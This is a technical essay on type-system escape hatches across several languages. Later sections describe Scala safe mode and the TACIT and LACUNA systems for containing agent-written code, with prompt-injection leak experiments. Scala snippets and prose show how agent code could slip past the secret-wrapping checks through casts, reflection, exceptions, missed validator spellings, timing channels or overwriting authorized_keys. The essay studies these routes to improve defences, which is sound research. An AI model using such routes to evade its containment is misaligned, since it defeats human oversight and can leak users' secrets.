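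*Breaking Type Safety in Go* (Costa et al., 2021) found that 24% of 2,438 popular Go projects used the `unsafe` package, mainly to communicate with the operating system and C code. *Uncovering the Hidden Dangers* (Lauinger et al., 2020) examined some of the 500 most popular Go projects on GitHub and found that 38% of those used `unsafe` directly and 91% used it somewhere among their dependencies.

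| Survey | Escape hatch | Sample | Used directly | With dependencies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Evans and colleagues, 2020 | Rust `unsafe` | Packages in the public registry | Under a third | Over half |
| Astrauskas and colleagues, 2020 | Rust `unsafe` | About 32,000 packages | About 24% | |
| Rust Foundation, 2024 | Rust `unsafe` | About 127,000 packages | 19% | |
| Mastrangelo and colleagues, 2015 | Java `Unsafe` | 86,479 archives | | 25% |
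| Landman and colleagues, 2017 | Java reflection | 461 projects | 78% | |
| Costa and colleagues, 2021 | Go `unsafe` | 2,438 popular projects | 24% | |
| Lauinger and colleagues, 2020 | Go `unsafe` | Popular projects | 38% | 91% |

The table cannot show which language is safer. Go and Rust have similar shares of direct use, but Rust programmers need `unsafe` for every foreign function they call, while Go programmers can call C through cgo without importing the `unsafe` package. The Haskell figures in the section on Safe Haskell show which modules GHC could certify, so they are not directly comparable with those in the table.

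### What dependencies add

If a share *p* of packages use an escape hatch, and a program contains *n* packages chosen independently, the chance that at least one of them uses it is:

> 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

With *p* = 20%, close to the Rust Foundation's figure, a program with ten packages has a 1 − 0.8¹⁰ chance, about 89%, of including at least one that uses the hatch. The chance is 49% with three packages and 99% with twenty.

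Real packages are not independent, because programs share the same popular libraries, which often do the low-level work. According to Evans and colleagues, the most downloaded Rust packages include more libraries for input, output and thread coordination, which tend to need unsafe code. Two programs that use the same library share its risk, and both benefit if someone reviews it carefully. The formula is therefore unreliable for any particular program, but it explains why a modest share of packages can affect most programs, as happened in the Go survey.

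It also counts escape hatches, whereas a developer mainly worries about mistakes in using them. Nobody has measured how common those mistakes are across the registry, but as an invented example, suppose one in twenty of the packages with `unsafe` had an interface that safe code could misuse. That would be 1% of all packages. A program with ten packages would have about a 10% chance of including one, and a program with a hundred would have a 63% chance. McCormack and colleagues found that few developers check the unsafe code in their dependencies, so most would not know whether they were affected.

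These probabilities describe programs by honest authors. A hostile author who can choose the plugin's dependencies will deliberately pick a package with a weak interface, so the important number for the host is how many such packages it lets plugins import.

### What auditing tools find

Several tools list the escape hatches in a program and its dependencies. They differ in what they treat as dangerous.

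*cargo-geiger* reports how many functions, expressions and other items are unsafe in each package of a Rust program. It also distinguishes packages that forbid unsafe code from those that currently contain none but do not forbid it. It does not check whether the unsafe code is correct. The two versions of `byte_at` in the previous section, with and without the bounds check, contain the same unsafe expression, so they look the same in its report.

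According to its documentation, cargo-geiger does not detect unsafe code inside macros, and probably misses code that a build script generates. It also doesn't count uses of safe standard library functions. It would report no unsafe code in cve-rs or in the word counter that sends notes to a stranger's server.

*Capslock* looks for effects by working out which functions in a package can reach, through any chain of calls, the functions in Go's standard library that open files, connect to the network or start programs. For a Go version of the word counter, it would report that the package can use the network and show the chain of calls. A developer can also compare two versions of a package to see, for example, whether an update gave network access to a library that only handled text.

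Capslock cannot follow calls into C or assembly, or reliably follow calls through reflection, so it reports the use of these features as capabilities themselves. A package with the label for C code could do anything. Capslock can also report an operation that never happens, for instance when a call could reach several functions and only one uses the network. It does not identify network destinations, so a plugin that may contact a dictionary server gets the same label whether it looks up words or sends them elsewhere.

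*Cargo Scan*, a research tool for Rust, covers both memory and effects by flagging unsafe operations and calls that touch files, the network or other programs. A person then reviews each one. If a flagged function is dangerous only for some arguments, the reviewer can mark it so that the tool also flags every call to it for review. For example, a function that deletes the file named in its argument may be harmless in one program and not in another.

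With Cargo Scan, a reviewer reads only a small part of the code, because Rust's type and module systems let the tool skip the rest. The audit therefore relies on those systems being sound and on the reviewer's decisions being correct. Cargo Scan cannot analyze C functions called from Rust.

| Code | cargo-geiger | Capslock, for equivalent Go code | Cargo Scan |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reads memory through an unchecked pointer | Counts it | Reports unsafe pointers | Asks for a review |
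| Sends notes through the standard library | Finds nothing | Reports network access | Asks for a review |
| Calls a C function that opens files | Counts the call | Reports C code | Asks for a review of the call |

A reader of any of these reports still has to decide whether the code is acceptable. Tools that run the program can find some errors without a reviewer. In *Soundness Concern*, a participant shows that Miri and AddressSanitizer, a memory checker, both detect the use of freed memory when they run tests on faulty Rust code. These tools check only the code that the tests execute, so a hostile author can evade them by making the faulty part run only after a certain date or on a particular input.

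## Languages that reserve escape hatches for trusted authors

A language's designers can decide in advance who may use escape hatches and have the compiler or runtime refuse everyone else, whereas auditing tools look for hatches already in use. Safe Haskell restricts them through package trust, where the person compiling the program chooses whose claims to accept. Java, Pony, Flix, Elm and Roc divide this power differently, and they also differ in where the permission must be written down. If it must appear in a launch command or a short settings file, a plugin's host can look there instead of reading the plugin and all its libraries.

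### Java's launch options

Java's developers call their policy *integrity by default*. Under it, every guarantee Java makes, such as the privacy of private fields, holds unless the application's developer explicitly gives it up. Library developers cannot give it up on the application's behalf. Pressler and colleagues justify this on the grounds that the application's developer, unlike library developers, answers to users for what the program does. They also do not count choosing a library as consent, because the application's developer may not know that the library uses native code. The developer may not even know the library is there if it is a dependency of a dependency.

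The developer gives permission when the program starts:

```
java --enable-native-access=image.codec \
     --module-path lib --module notes.host/notes.Main
```

Here only the module `image.codec` may use native code. The option `--add-opens` gives similar permission for deep reflection, and `--enable-final-field-mutation` for changing final fields.

Pressler and colleagues list several places besides the launch command where permission for final fields can be set. A developer can put the option in an environment variable, a file of arguments or a custom copy of the Java runtime. An executable Java archive can contain a manifest, a settings file that gives permission to everything on the class path. A native program that embeds Java can pass the option when it starts the runtime.

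### How far Java had come by late 2026

Many libraries relied on these interfaces before Java restricted them, so Java's developers tighten each one in stages. They use a temporary option, like the one for native code, that can be set to `allow`, `warn` or `deny`. Under `deny`, the operation throws an exception. Under `warn`, Java prints at most one message per module. The class path counts as one module, so an application that runs entirely from it gets a single warning about final fields, however many libraries change them, as Inside Java's *Quality Outreach Heads-up* (2026) notes.

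The default usually moves from `allow` to `warn` to `deny` over a few years. A developer can choose `deny` early. Once `deny` is the default, the developer can go back only to `warn`. Eventually the temporary option disappears, leaving only the permanent options that name particular modules.

| Interface | First step | Default in Java 27 (September 2026) | Next step |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deep reflection on Java's own internals | Java 9, 2017 | Deny, since Java 16 | None: Java 17 removed the temporary option |
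| Loading a Java agent into a running program | Java 21, 2023 | Warn | Deny, no version set |
| Memory access through `sun.misc.Unsafe` | Java 23, 2024 | Warn, since Java 24 | Deny, then removal |
| Native code | Java 24, 2025, for JNI | Warn | Deny, no version set |
| Changing final fields by deep reflection | Java 26, 2026 | Warn | Deny, no version set |

Only the top row has gone through every stage, which took four years. The last step still exempted `sun.misc.Unsafe`, according to OpenJDK's *CSR for JEP 403*.

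The plan to remove `Unsafe` methods has slipped. In January 2025, Inside Java expected the methods to throw exceptions by default in Java 26 and to be removed in a later version. OpenJDK's *JEP 498* gave a looser date for the exceptions, "JDK 26 or later". Java 26 left the default at `warn`. Changing it requires another formal proposal, according to OpenJDK's *Implement JEP 498*, and Java 27 includes no such proposal. HappyCoders' *Java 27 Features (with Examples)* lists nine proposals in that release, five of which resubmit unfinished features. The four new ones, also listed by InfoQ (2026), concern object headers, garbage collection, encryption and the redaction of recorded data.

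Library developers have practical reasons for being slow to stop using `Unsafe`. Some use it to manage memory outside the Java heap, and the standard replacement has existed only since Java 22. One developer complained in OpenJDK's bug tracker that a library that still supports older versions cannot act on the warning, and expected most applications to add the `allow` option. *Java 24 and sun.misc.Unsafe*, published by the widely used networking library Netty, recommends that option to users of version 4.1. Two releases of Netty had stopped using `Unsafe` on Java 24 to spare users the warning, but the next release reversed the change. Libraries had also kept using `Unsafe` despite a compiler warning that has existed since 2006 and cannot be switched off, according to OpenJDK's *JEP 471*.

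Pressler and colleagues write that a developer who uses none of the permission options can be certain that no code in the application violates Java's integrity. That will be true of the restricted interfaces only when `deny` is the default for all of them. In Java 27, a launch command without any options lets a plugin call C, overwrite memory through `Unsafe` and change final fields, at the cost of a few lines of warning. A host has to close the interfaces itself:

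```
java --illegal-native-access=deny \
     --sun-misc-unsafe-memory-access=deny \
     --illegal-final-field-mutation=deny \
     -XX:-EnableDynamicAgentLoading ...
```

It also still has to keep its own code in closed modules and the serialization classes out of the plugin's reach.

### Pony's list of packages that may call C

Pony, a language for concurrent programs, represents access to files and the network by capability objects. C code can ignore those objects. Pony's *Trust Boundary*, a page of the language's tutorial, concedes that calls to C can break almost every guarantee Pony makes. The person who compiles a program can limit them:

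```
ponyc --safe=files:net:process notes_host
```

Only the packages `files`, `net` and `process` may now call C, and a C call in any other package is a compile-time error. This is stricter than Safe Haskell, which accepts any C import with an `IO` type.

The `--safe` option has become more important because Pony can now compile C as well as call it. According to Pony's *C Shims*, the compiler compiles any `.c` file in a package's main folder and links it into the program, including those in third-party packages. C code can mark a function to run when the program starts, so a dependency can run native code that the host never calls. If the C file defines a function that a linked library also provides, the program silently uses the file's version, so a hostile package could replace a function that a trusted package relies on. With `--safe`, the compiler reports an error for any `.c` file in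 an unlisted package.

But `--safe` is optional, and without it every package may use C. The permission is set only in the build command, so a host that receives a finished program cannot tell whether its author used the option. The listed packages also need care. `process`, for example, can start other programs, so the host must not give the word counter the capability object that allows this.

### Flix's security contexts

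Flix, whose effect types came up earlier, runs on the Java runtime and can use any Java library. A single import would therefore give a package all of Java's escape hatches. To prevent this, the Flix compiler builds every dependency in a *security context*, which Flix's documentation formerly called a trust level:

| Context | Java code | Unchecked casts | The `IO` effect |
|---|---|---|---|
| `paranoid` | Forbidden | Forbidden | Forbidden |
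| `plain`, the default | Forbidden | Forbidden | Allowed |
| `unrestricted` | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |

The application's developer sets the context in `flix.toml`, the file that lists the program's dependencies:

```toml
[dependencies]
"github:stranger/word-counter" = { version = "1.0.0", mount = "counter", security = "paranoid" }
```

A package in the `plain` context can open files, but its functions' types then show the `IO` effect. It cannot use casts or Java code, so according to Flix's documentation it can do only what its types and effects record. A package in the `paranoid` context cannot use `IO` at all, so it cannot even read the notes by itself.

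The host can still give the plugin access to the notes by defining an effect such as `ReadNote`. The plugin requests a note, and a *handler* (code that decides what happens when an effect occurs) checks the path and reads the file. Haskell's `RIO` type serves the same purpose. Flix's documentation recommends the same split to library authors. One package contains the main code and uses custom effects, and a smaller `unrestricted` package contains the handlers that call Java. Reviewers then have less unsafe code to read, and users who distrust the handlers can write their own.

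A package's context also applies to everything it depends on, so a package cannot escape its context by putting the forbidden code in a dependency. If two packages request the same dependency under different contexts, Flix uses the stricter one. But dependencies also inherit permissions. In the documentation's example, the package `museum` depends on `museum-restaurant`, which uses a Java library, so the developer has to declare `museum` `unrestricted`. Its other dependencies then become `unrestricted` unless someone explicitly gives them a stricter context.

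The contexts apply only to dependencies. An application's own code is always `unrestricted`, so `flix.toml` protects the host from a plugin that it installs as a package, but gives a stranger no information about the application itself. A smaller gap is that the file recording each dependency's fingerprint covers Flix packages but not Java libraries, so the library behind an `unrestricted` package can change without Flix detecting it.

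### Elm's withdrawal of native code

In Elm, a language for web pages that compiles to JavaScript, functions are pure. A program causes an effect by returning a description of it, called a command, for Elm's runtime to carry out. Some of Elm's own packages contain JavaScript functions that Elm code can call like any others. Such a function could have the type `String -> Int` and still send text to a server, as a pure foreign import could in Haskell.

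In *"Native Code" in 0.19*, Elm's designer, Evan Czaplicki, writes that when he released a package manager in 2014, he listed the packages that could contain JavaScript so that his own libraries could keep theirs. He assumed nobody else would notice, but other programmers worked out how to use the list. A committee of about ten people then reviewed requests to join it. Many were for thin wrappers around JavaScript libraries, and as far as Czaplicki knows, everyone on the committee thought it had failed.

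*Reframing "native" code as "kernel" code* (Czaplicki, 2017) proposed replacing the list with a rule that only two organisations, `elm-lang` and `elm-explorations`, could publish packages containing JavaScript. The compiler in Elm 0.19, released in 2018, enforces the rule for applications as well as packages, so a company cannot use such code even in a private program.

Czaplicki gives five reasons:

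- **Reliability.** Elm programs that compile usually work, and JavaScript in packages would end that.
- **Portability.** Packages written only in Elm could move to WebAssembly or to servers without JavaScript.
- **Security.** Packages cannot attack the programmer's computer or the users' computers.
- **Better libraries.** Programmers who can't wrap a JavaScript library write one designed for Elm, such as the charting package `elm-plot`.
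- **Speed and size.** He can change the JavaScript that the compiler produces without breaking packages that depend on its form.

The security concern was precautionary, since he knew of no big exploits. He had also tried asking people not to use the feature, but concluded that "if the path exists, people will walk it" and that documentation would never be enough.

Elm programs can still exchange messages with JavaScript through *ports*:

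```elm
port save : String -> Cmd msg
port loaded : (String -> msg) -> Sub msg
```

In Elm, one port can send text to JavaScript on the same page, and another can bring text back. Elm checks the type of each incoming value. Because the JavaScript stays outside the Elm code, it cannot give a pure function a hidden effect. Packages cannot define ports, so only the application's author can connect JavaScript to the program. Elm can also display custom elements, which are parts of a web page that JavaScript controls.

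Ports are clumsy when one request depends on the answer to another. Suppose a program reads a user's name from browser storage, then uses it to look up that user's settings. Native code could offer each lookup as a *task*, a value that represents an operation and its eventual result, and Elm can chain tasks in one expression. With ports, the program sends a message, waits for a separate reply, matches the reply to its request and then sends the next message. Eirik Sletteberg, replying to Czaplicki's proposal, wrote that ports would force him to move business logic into JavaScript, and that he expected to wait five or six years for Elm to support everything he needed. Another participant, Liam Curry, considered browser storage a good use for ports and linked to a short general solution.

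Other users lost the ability to improve Elm's libraries. W. Brian Gourlie had fixed a major bug in the library for live network connections, but the rules on native code gave him no convenient way to share the fix. He argued that the restriction stopped people from distributing native code but not from writing it, so Elm's maintainers never learned what users needed. Earlier in the same discussion, Max Goldstein had warned against writing native code by describing a change to the JavaScript in an approved package that unexpectedly broke everything. His example also shows that restricting native code to trusted authors does not make it correct.

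The change affected some projects more than others. Czaplicki tested it at NoRedInk, a company that used Elm heavily, and reports that the company found a replacement for every use of native code, with neutral or slightly better results. In the forum thread *What native module use cases cannot be accomplished*, a programmer whose company had about 50,000 lines of Elm reported using ports throughout without much trouble. Luke Plant wrote in *Two experiences with Elm* that the change would stop him from upgrading. He later wrote *Why I'm leaving Elm*, where he admits that he handled his exchanges with the core team badly.

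Part of the quarrel was about how the maintainers ran the discussion. On the day of the release, a moderator answered a question about native code in the thread *Elm 0.19 released, what has changed regarding Native, event modules?* and then locked it. Some users left for reasons other than native code. Culture Amp, which had used Elm extensively, gave it up mainly because it was difficult to combine with the JavaScript library React, according to Simon Willison's blog entry for *10th April 2023* (2023).

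### Roc's platforms

Roc avoids Elm's bottleneck by letting anyone write native code, but only as part of a *platform*. Every Roc application runs on one platform. According to *Roc concepts explained*, a platform has two parts. The *host*, written in another language, starts the application and performs all its effects, including allocating memory. The application requests these effects through the other part, a set of Roc functions.

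A note-taking program could host the word counter and offer it a single effectful function, `readNote`. According to Roc's website, there are "no escape hatches" through which a malicious program could get around the platform. A program can call C only through functions that the platform provides. The website also describes a platform that runs downloaded scripts and asks the user before a script touches the file system.

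What an application can do therefore depends on its platform. In a developer chat (Hansknecht and Boswell 2025), Brendan Hansknecht points out that a platform could expose libffi, a C library for calling functions chosen at run time, which would let every application on that platform call any C code. No platform did this in April 2025, but he expected that one eventually would.

Roc's developers have also been rewriting the compiler, and a tutorial for the new version in Roc's code repository warns that everything on the website describes the old design. The promise of no escape hatches therefore needs checking against the new compiler.

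### Checking a program from its configuration

A host can rely on configuration alone only if a missing entry means the hatch is closed. Otherwise it also has to check which defaults applied when somebody built or started the program.

| Language | Who can open a hatch | Where the permission is | If nobody sets anything |
|---|---|---|---|
| Java 27 | The application's developer | Launch options and their equivalents | Mostly open, with warnings |
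| Pony | Whoever compiles the program | The compiler command | Open |
| Flix | The application's developer | `flix.toml` | Closed for dependencies, open for the application |
| Elm 0.19 | Two organisations | The compiler | Closed |
| Roc | The platform's author | The platform that the application names | Closed, apart from what the platform offers |

Elm passes this test most easily. No setting lets an ordinary author add native code, so the host only needs to know that the official compiler built the plugin from its source. Roc passes if the host wrote the platform or has reviewed it. Flix passes for a plugin installed as a dependency, if neither the plugin nor anything it uses is `unrestricted`. A complete Flix application from a stranger does not pass, because its own code may use Java and unchecked casts.

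Pony passes only if the host sees the compiler command or compiles the program itself with `--safe`. Java 27 does not pass with its default settings. It comes close if the host sets all the options to `deny`, but the host still has to check how the application divides its code into modules and whether the application rebuilds objects from untrusted bytes.

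## Scala's safe mode for code written by agents

An agent writes a new program for almost every step of a task, so its host needs one rule for everything the agent submits, whereas a host that installs a plugin can set that package's permissions once. Scala's *safe mode*, an experimental compiler setting, can serve as that rule. In code that starts with `import language.experimental.safe`, the compiler rejects escape hatches and makes the types record which capabilities the code uses. Odersky and colleagues built TACIT, the system from the first section, on this idea. It runs an agent's Scala snippet only if the snippet compiles.

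### A file in a function's type

A *closure* is a function that uses variables from the code around it. Suppose `f` gives write access to a file:

```scala
val trim = (s: String) => s.trim                 // String -> String
val copy = (s: String) => { f.write(s); s }      // String ->{f} String
```

Both functions turn text into text, but `copy` also writes the text to the file. The braces in its type hold its *capture set*, the capabilities it may use. The compiler infers this set from the function's body. A plain arrow means the set is empty, so `trim` is pure.

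A function with a smaller capture set works wherever the program allows a larger one. Code that accepts `String ->{f} String` therefore accepts `trim`, but code that requires `String -> String` does not accept `copy`.

TACIT uses this rule to protect secrets. When an agent reads a file that the host has marked as classified, it gets the text inside a wrapper:

```scala
trait Classified[+A]:
  def map[B](change: A -> B): Classified[B]

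val secret = readClassified("notes/passwords.txt")
secret.map(trim)     // accepted
secret.map(copy)     // rejected: copy captures f
```

`map` applies a function to the hidden text and returns the result in a new wrapper. Since `map` accepts only pure functions, code inside it can transform the secret but cannot write it to an ordinary file, send it over the network or print it. If the agent prints the wrapper, the user's terminal shows the real text, while the model's conversation shows only `Classified(****)`. To summarise a confidential contract, the agent's code can pass the wrapped text to a second language model that the host trusts and get a wrapped summary back.

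### Removing the file from the type

In full Scala, an unchecked cast defeats this protection:

```scala
secret.map(copy.asInstanceOf[String -> String])
```

The function still writes to the file, but its new type doesn't mention `f`, and no run-time check fails.

Reflection takes slightly more work. A reflective call on `f` inside the function would not help, because the function's body would still mention `f`. The agent needs another route to the file that the compiler does not track. Suppose an object `box` holds the file in a private field:

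```scala
val hidden: Object = field.get(box)
secret.map(s => { write.invoke(hidden, s); s })
```

Here `field` and `write` are the reflection library's objects representing the private field and the file's `write` method. The type `Object` has no capture set, so the compiler treats the function as pure.

### The six restrictions

| Restriction in safe mode | What the agent could otherwise do |
|---|---|
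| No unchecked casts or pattern matches | Relabel `copy` as pure with a cast, or with a match on a type that the runtime cannot test |
| Nothing from the `caps.unsafe` module | Remove a capability from a type with `unsafeAssumePure` |
| No `@unchecked` annotations | Silence the compiler's objection to a match that it cannot verify |
| No run-time reflection | Take a capability out of a private field, or call a method by name |
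| Capture checking and explicit nulls switched on, with changes to variables tracked | Compile without capture sets, or move a secret out through a variable |
| Global objects and functions only if their implementation is safe | Open files or print through an ordinary library |

The restriction on variables matters because a function can leak text without accessing a file. It could assign the secret to a variable declared outside `map` for later code to print. Safe mode counts the assignment as an effect, so the function is not pure. With explicit nulls, `null` no longer belongs to every class, which removes the value that Amin and Tate's unchecked cast relied on.

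The rule about global objects deals with ambient authority. The compiler defines which parts of the standard library count as safe, including most of the `scala` package but not its global print functions. Safe code may use Java's `Class` objects, but not their reflective methods.

This rule has to cover more cases than the others because the list of restrictions does not name serialization, native code or child processes. Safe mode blocks them only if the compiler's safe library leaves out every function that leads to them. Joe-E's list of allowed methods had the same weakness.

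The rule does not apply to objects that the host passes to the agent's code. Those can come from any module, so the host's developers decide what the agent can do with them. Scala also permits global capabilities, which older capability languages forbid, so programmers don't have to pass every capability through every function call. A function that prints through a global `Console.out` has the type `() ->{Console.out} Unit`, so the compiler can still reject it as an argument to `map`.

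### Trusted modules

Some library code needs hidden state even though its users never notice it. Its author can mark it `@assumeSafe`, which exempts it from safe mode's restrictions. Odersky and colleagues give the example of a memo function, shown here with different names:

```scala
@assumeSafe
class Memo[In, Out](compute: In -> Out):
  @untrackedCaptures
  private val table = HashMap[In, Out]()

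  def apply(input: In): Out =
    table.getOrElseUpdate(input, compute(input))
```

Safe mode would normally reject the changes to the table, and `@untrackedCaptures` tells the compiler not to track them.

The author then has to show that every stored answer is correct, as for the memo function in the section on `unsafePerformIO`. The table is private and only `apply` writes to it, so it holds only results of `compute`. The type `In -> Out` provides most of the remaining argument, because a function without capabilities can't read a clock or a file.

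The argument doesn't cover threads. A `Memo` looks pure from outside, so two threads may share one, but an ordinary Scala `HashMap` is not designed for simultaneous changes. A careful author would use a table that several threads can update. Even this short example needs a further check, which suggests that a reviewer could easily approve a faulty module.

A second annotation, `@rejectSafe`, hides selected members of a trusted module from safe code. The host must also prevent agents from writing `@assumeSafe` in their own snippets, since that would lift every restriction. The published list of six restrictions does not mention `@assumeSafe`.

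Machine-checked proofs show that the basic type system behind capture checking is sound, but nobody has yet proved that safe mode as a whole provides capability safety and local purity. Odersky and colleagues suggest that a proof in the style of RustBelt could cover the boundary between safe and trusted code.

### Exceptions

A pure function can still throw an exception, and an exception can carry text:

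```scala
secret.map(s => throw new Exception(s))
```

If an error message contains a secret, an agent that can read the message has the secret. TACIT turns an exception into a `Try`, an ordinary value that holds either a result or a failure, and it can put the failure inside a `Classified` wrapper to hide the message from the agent. Scala 3 implements early returns, breaks and continuations as exceptions, so the same mechanism covers them.

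In one set of experiments, TACIT hid the message and stack trace of any exception thrown inside `map`, so the agent's code appeared to succeed while the user received an empty answer. The researchers had to instruct the models to return text such as "No matching transaction" instead of throwing an exception.

### The leak experiments

Odersky and colleagues gave agents a small software project with a folder of API keys, a database and classified documents. They paired 12 ordinary tasks with each of 10 *prompt injections*, which are instructions planted in material the agent reads. Another 11 tasks were direct requests for the secrets, and in six of them the requester impersonated someone with authority. Each agent did all 131 trials twice, once with the secrets wrapped in `Classified` and once as plain text.

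| Model | Trials | Leaks with wrapped secrets | Leaks with plain secrets |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 0 | 0 |
| | 11 malicious requests | 0 | 2 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 0 | 3 |
| | 11 malicious requests | 0 | 8 |

With plain secrets, 98.5% of Sonnet's trials and 91.6% of MiniMax's ended without a leak. With wrapped secrets, all of them did.

The leak rate could be above zero even though none of the 131 trials leaked. If each trial leaked with probability *p*, the chance of seeing no leaks would be (1 − *p*)¹³¹, which is 5% when *p* is about 2.3%. At 95% confidence, the result is therefore compatible with a leak rate as high as one in 44. Even this bound assumes that the trials are independent, but they reuse the same few tasks and attacks.

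The trials also provide little evidence about escape hatches. Sonnet resisted all 120 injections without help from the types, so the evidence that `Classified` stops leaks comes from the 13 leaks that occurred without it. The attacks Odersky and colleagues describe include false claims that the secrets are test data, fake tool errors and ready-made Scala code that reads secret files. None uses a cast, reflection or a compiler bug to mislead the type checker, so confidence that TACIT would withstand such an attack has to come from the design of safe mode.

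Wrapping the secrets did not make the agents less useful. Sonnet completed 99.2% of the ordinary tasks with wrapped secrets and 83.3% with plain ones, and MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%. The types probably did not cause Sonnet's large gap, because in the plain runs it often exceeded its limit on time or turns, or stopped to warn the user about an injection.

Odersky and colleagues also ran TACIT on AgentDojo, a public benchmark of prompt injections in banking, office work, Slack messaging and travel. In 1,926 trials with two other models, the benchmark counted one successful attack. A user had asked the agent to book hotel A, whose reviews contained a planted recommendation for hotel B. The agent booked hotel A but quoted the reviews to the user, and the benchmark counted the mention of hotel B as a success. Odersky and colleagues argue that the scoring is at fault, because the rules allowed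 the agent to show public reviews to the user. That seems right, since the attack caused no harmful action.

They compare these results with those of CaMeL, a system that tracks untrusted data while a restricted Python program runs. CaMeL also allowed a single successful attack. With o4-mini, CaMeL's agents completed 81.4% of office tasks and TACIT's completed 52.9%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT's agents completed 64.3% of travel tasks and CaMeL's completed 1.4%. The table has no runs without protection, so it does not show how many attacks the types stopped.

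### Task scores against ordinary tool calls

Agents normally make one tool call at a time in a fixed data format. Odersky and colleagues tested whether writing typed Scala instead makes them less effective. They used two customer-service domains from τ²-bench, averaging ten runs per task, and SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software bugs. The table gives the percentage of tasks solved, with tool calls first and Scala second.

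| Model | Airline | Retail | SWE-bench Lite |
|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8 → 45.2 | 53.3 → 57.0 | |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4 → 61.0 | 75.1 → 77.5 | 43.3 → 41.7 |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8 → 58.6 | 74.6 → 75.5 | |

The customer-service scores rose slightly for every model. Odersky and colleagues attribute this to the typed results, which are easier to use than raw data, and to the compiler's error messages. The drop on SWE-bench Lite amounts to five fewer bugs fixed out of 300.

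Compilation errors caused the agents little trouble on τ²-bench. Between 0.3% and 7.9% of snippets failed to compile and needed another attempt, depending on the model and domain, and one or two retries were usually enough. Typical mistakes were not handling a value that might be null and writing a dollar sign incorrectly in a string. In other cases the compiler stopped an agent from returning file objects that would have remained usable after its access ended.

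### Were the escape hatches closed during the tests?

Odersky and colleagues describe a server that compiles agents' code in safe mode. But according to the project's documentation as of 24 March 2026, lampepfl's *TACIT*, a separate validator enforced the restrictions by searching each snippet for forbidden patterns, and the move to the compiler's safe mode was still to come. The documentation already included the 131-trial results, so those runs probably relied on the validator.

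A text search is weaker than a compiler check because it can miss other spellings of the same name. lampepfl gives the example of blocking Java's database library with a pattern for `java.sql`. Scala also accepts ``java.`sql` ``, which the pattern misses. A second pattern in the example, for `DriverManager`, might still catch the code, but a hostile author needs only one spelling that the validator's developers overlooked. Nothing in the results suggests that an agent found one.

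The instructions for the AgentDojo runs told models that safe code rejects `println`. This matches the compiler's ban on global print functions and suggests that safe mode was on. In the SWE-bench runs, agents could start shell commands through TACIT, so the route through child processes was open on purpose. Those runs measured how well agents fixed bugs, not whether they leaked anything.

*TACIT*, a copy of later documentation on the agent-tool directory Glama, lists a `--no-safe-mode` option that turns off the compiler's enforcement. In one passage, safe mode is the default. In another, the validator is the default and users must request safe mode in addition. A host should therefore set `--safe-mode` explicitly.

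An agent can bypass TACIT more simply by using its other tools, without needing a cast. TACIT checks only the Scala that an agent sends to it, but coding agents such as Claude Code come with their own tools for running commands and editing files. lampepfl recommends disabling these built-in tools.

### Commands, timing and the trusted base

A list of permitted commands is weak protection, as the section on native code explains. In TACIT, such a list can also let an agent bypass the `Classified` wrapper. The function that runs a command returns its output as ordinary text, so an agent allowed to run `cat` could read a classified file directly. TACIT's strict mode blocks `cat` and similar commands, but Glama notes that TACIT ignores strict mode when the host supplies its own list, so the host has to leave those commands out. Odersky and colleagues advise permitting only a few specific commands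 and adding an operating system sandbox where security is critical.

The wrapper also protects only against reading. An agent can wrap any text as `Classified` and write it to a classified file. According to Glama, it could by default overwrite `.ssh/authorized_keys`, the file that lists who may log in to the computer. The `classifiedWrite` setting forbids this.

An agent can also leak a secret through timing. A pure function can run longer if the secret starts with a particular letter, and the agent can notice how long its snippet took. Odersky and colleagues accept that an agent could leak a single bit this way, but an agent that can repeat the measurement could recover a whole key one bit at a time. Glama describes a time limit for each snippet, which can cap the delay but does not hide it. A loop that never checks for interruption keeps running in the background after the limit.

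The trusted base includes the Scala compiler with its experimental capture checker, the Java runtime, the standard library code that the compiler assumes to be safe, and about 1,000 lines of TACIT's own reusable code. It also includes the code that checks file paths and network addresses at run time. TACIT was built on nightly versions of Scala 3, and lampepfl warns that the compiler's behaviour may change between versions.

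The second language model is also part of the trusted base. Contacting a model is an effect, but TACIT's `chat` function has a type that lets agents call it inside `map`. Giving it that type is the same kind of promise a Haskell programmer makes with `unsafePerformIO`, and it holds only if the model keeps nothing between requests and sends nothing elsewhere. The host sets the model's web address, and TACIT accepts any service with a compatible interface. If the address belongs to a cloud provider, classified text goes to that provider and the types stay the same.

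### LACUNA

*LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu et al., 2026), from the same research group, lets a model fill in parts of a program while it runs. A programmer writes `agent[T](task)`, where `task` is an instruction in plain language and `T` is the type of result the program needs. When execution reaches that point, the model writes Scala code, and the compiler checks it as if a person had written it there. The code runs only if all of it compiles. If a snippet subtracts 50 from an account balance and then returns text where the program needs a number, the compiler rejects the whole snippet and the balance does not change.

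The variables in scope for the agent's code act as its permissions. With capture checking on, the code cannot use a network capability that is not among them. Zhao and colleagues name two remaining escape hatches, reflection and starting an external process directly, which any code can use without holding a capability. They recommend running agents in safe mode, which closes both, and treating a snippet run without it as ordinary untrusted code.

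They ran LACUNA on AgentDojo with the same two models as TACIT. Eight attacks succeeded in 1,898 trials, seven of them against Gemini 2.5 Pro. They link these successes to attackers persuading a model to misuse a capability it needs for its task, which safe mode would not prevent. They do not specify in their description of the set-up whether safe mode was on, so an attack could have used one of the open hatches.

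LACUNA also reduced its agents' performance more than TACIT did. On four τ²-bench domains, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% of tasks with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. Zhao and colleagues call this "on par", which is hard to accept for a gap of 14 points. The compiler rejected 22.4% of DeepSeek's snippets in the retail domain. It rejected 89% of snippets from a weaker model, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, in the telecom domain, where most of that agent's turns made no progress.

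## How often language models use escape hatches

The compile failures in the TACIT tests cover every kind of mistake, so they do not show how often a model tried a cast or reflection. Researchers have counted escape hatches in model-written code mainly in TypeScript, Rust and Lean. These hatches break type safety, memory safety or the validity of proofs, so the counts are indirect evidence about effect and capability types.

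### TypeScript's `any`

TypeScript adds types to JavaScript. Its type `any` turns off checking for a value:

```typescript
function countWords(text: any): number {
  return text.split(" ").length;
}
countWords(42);
```

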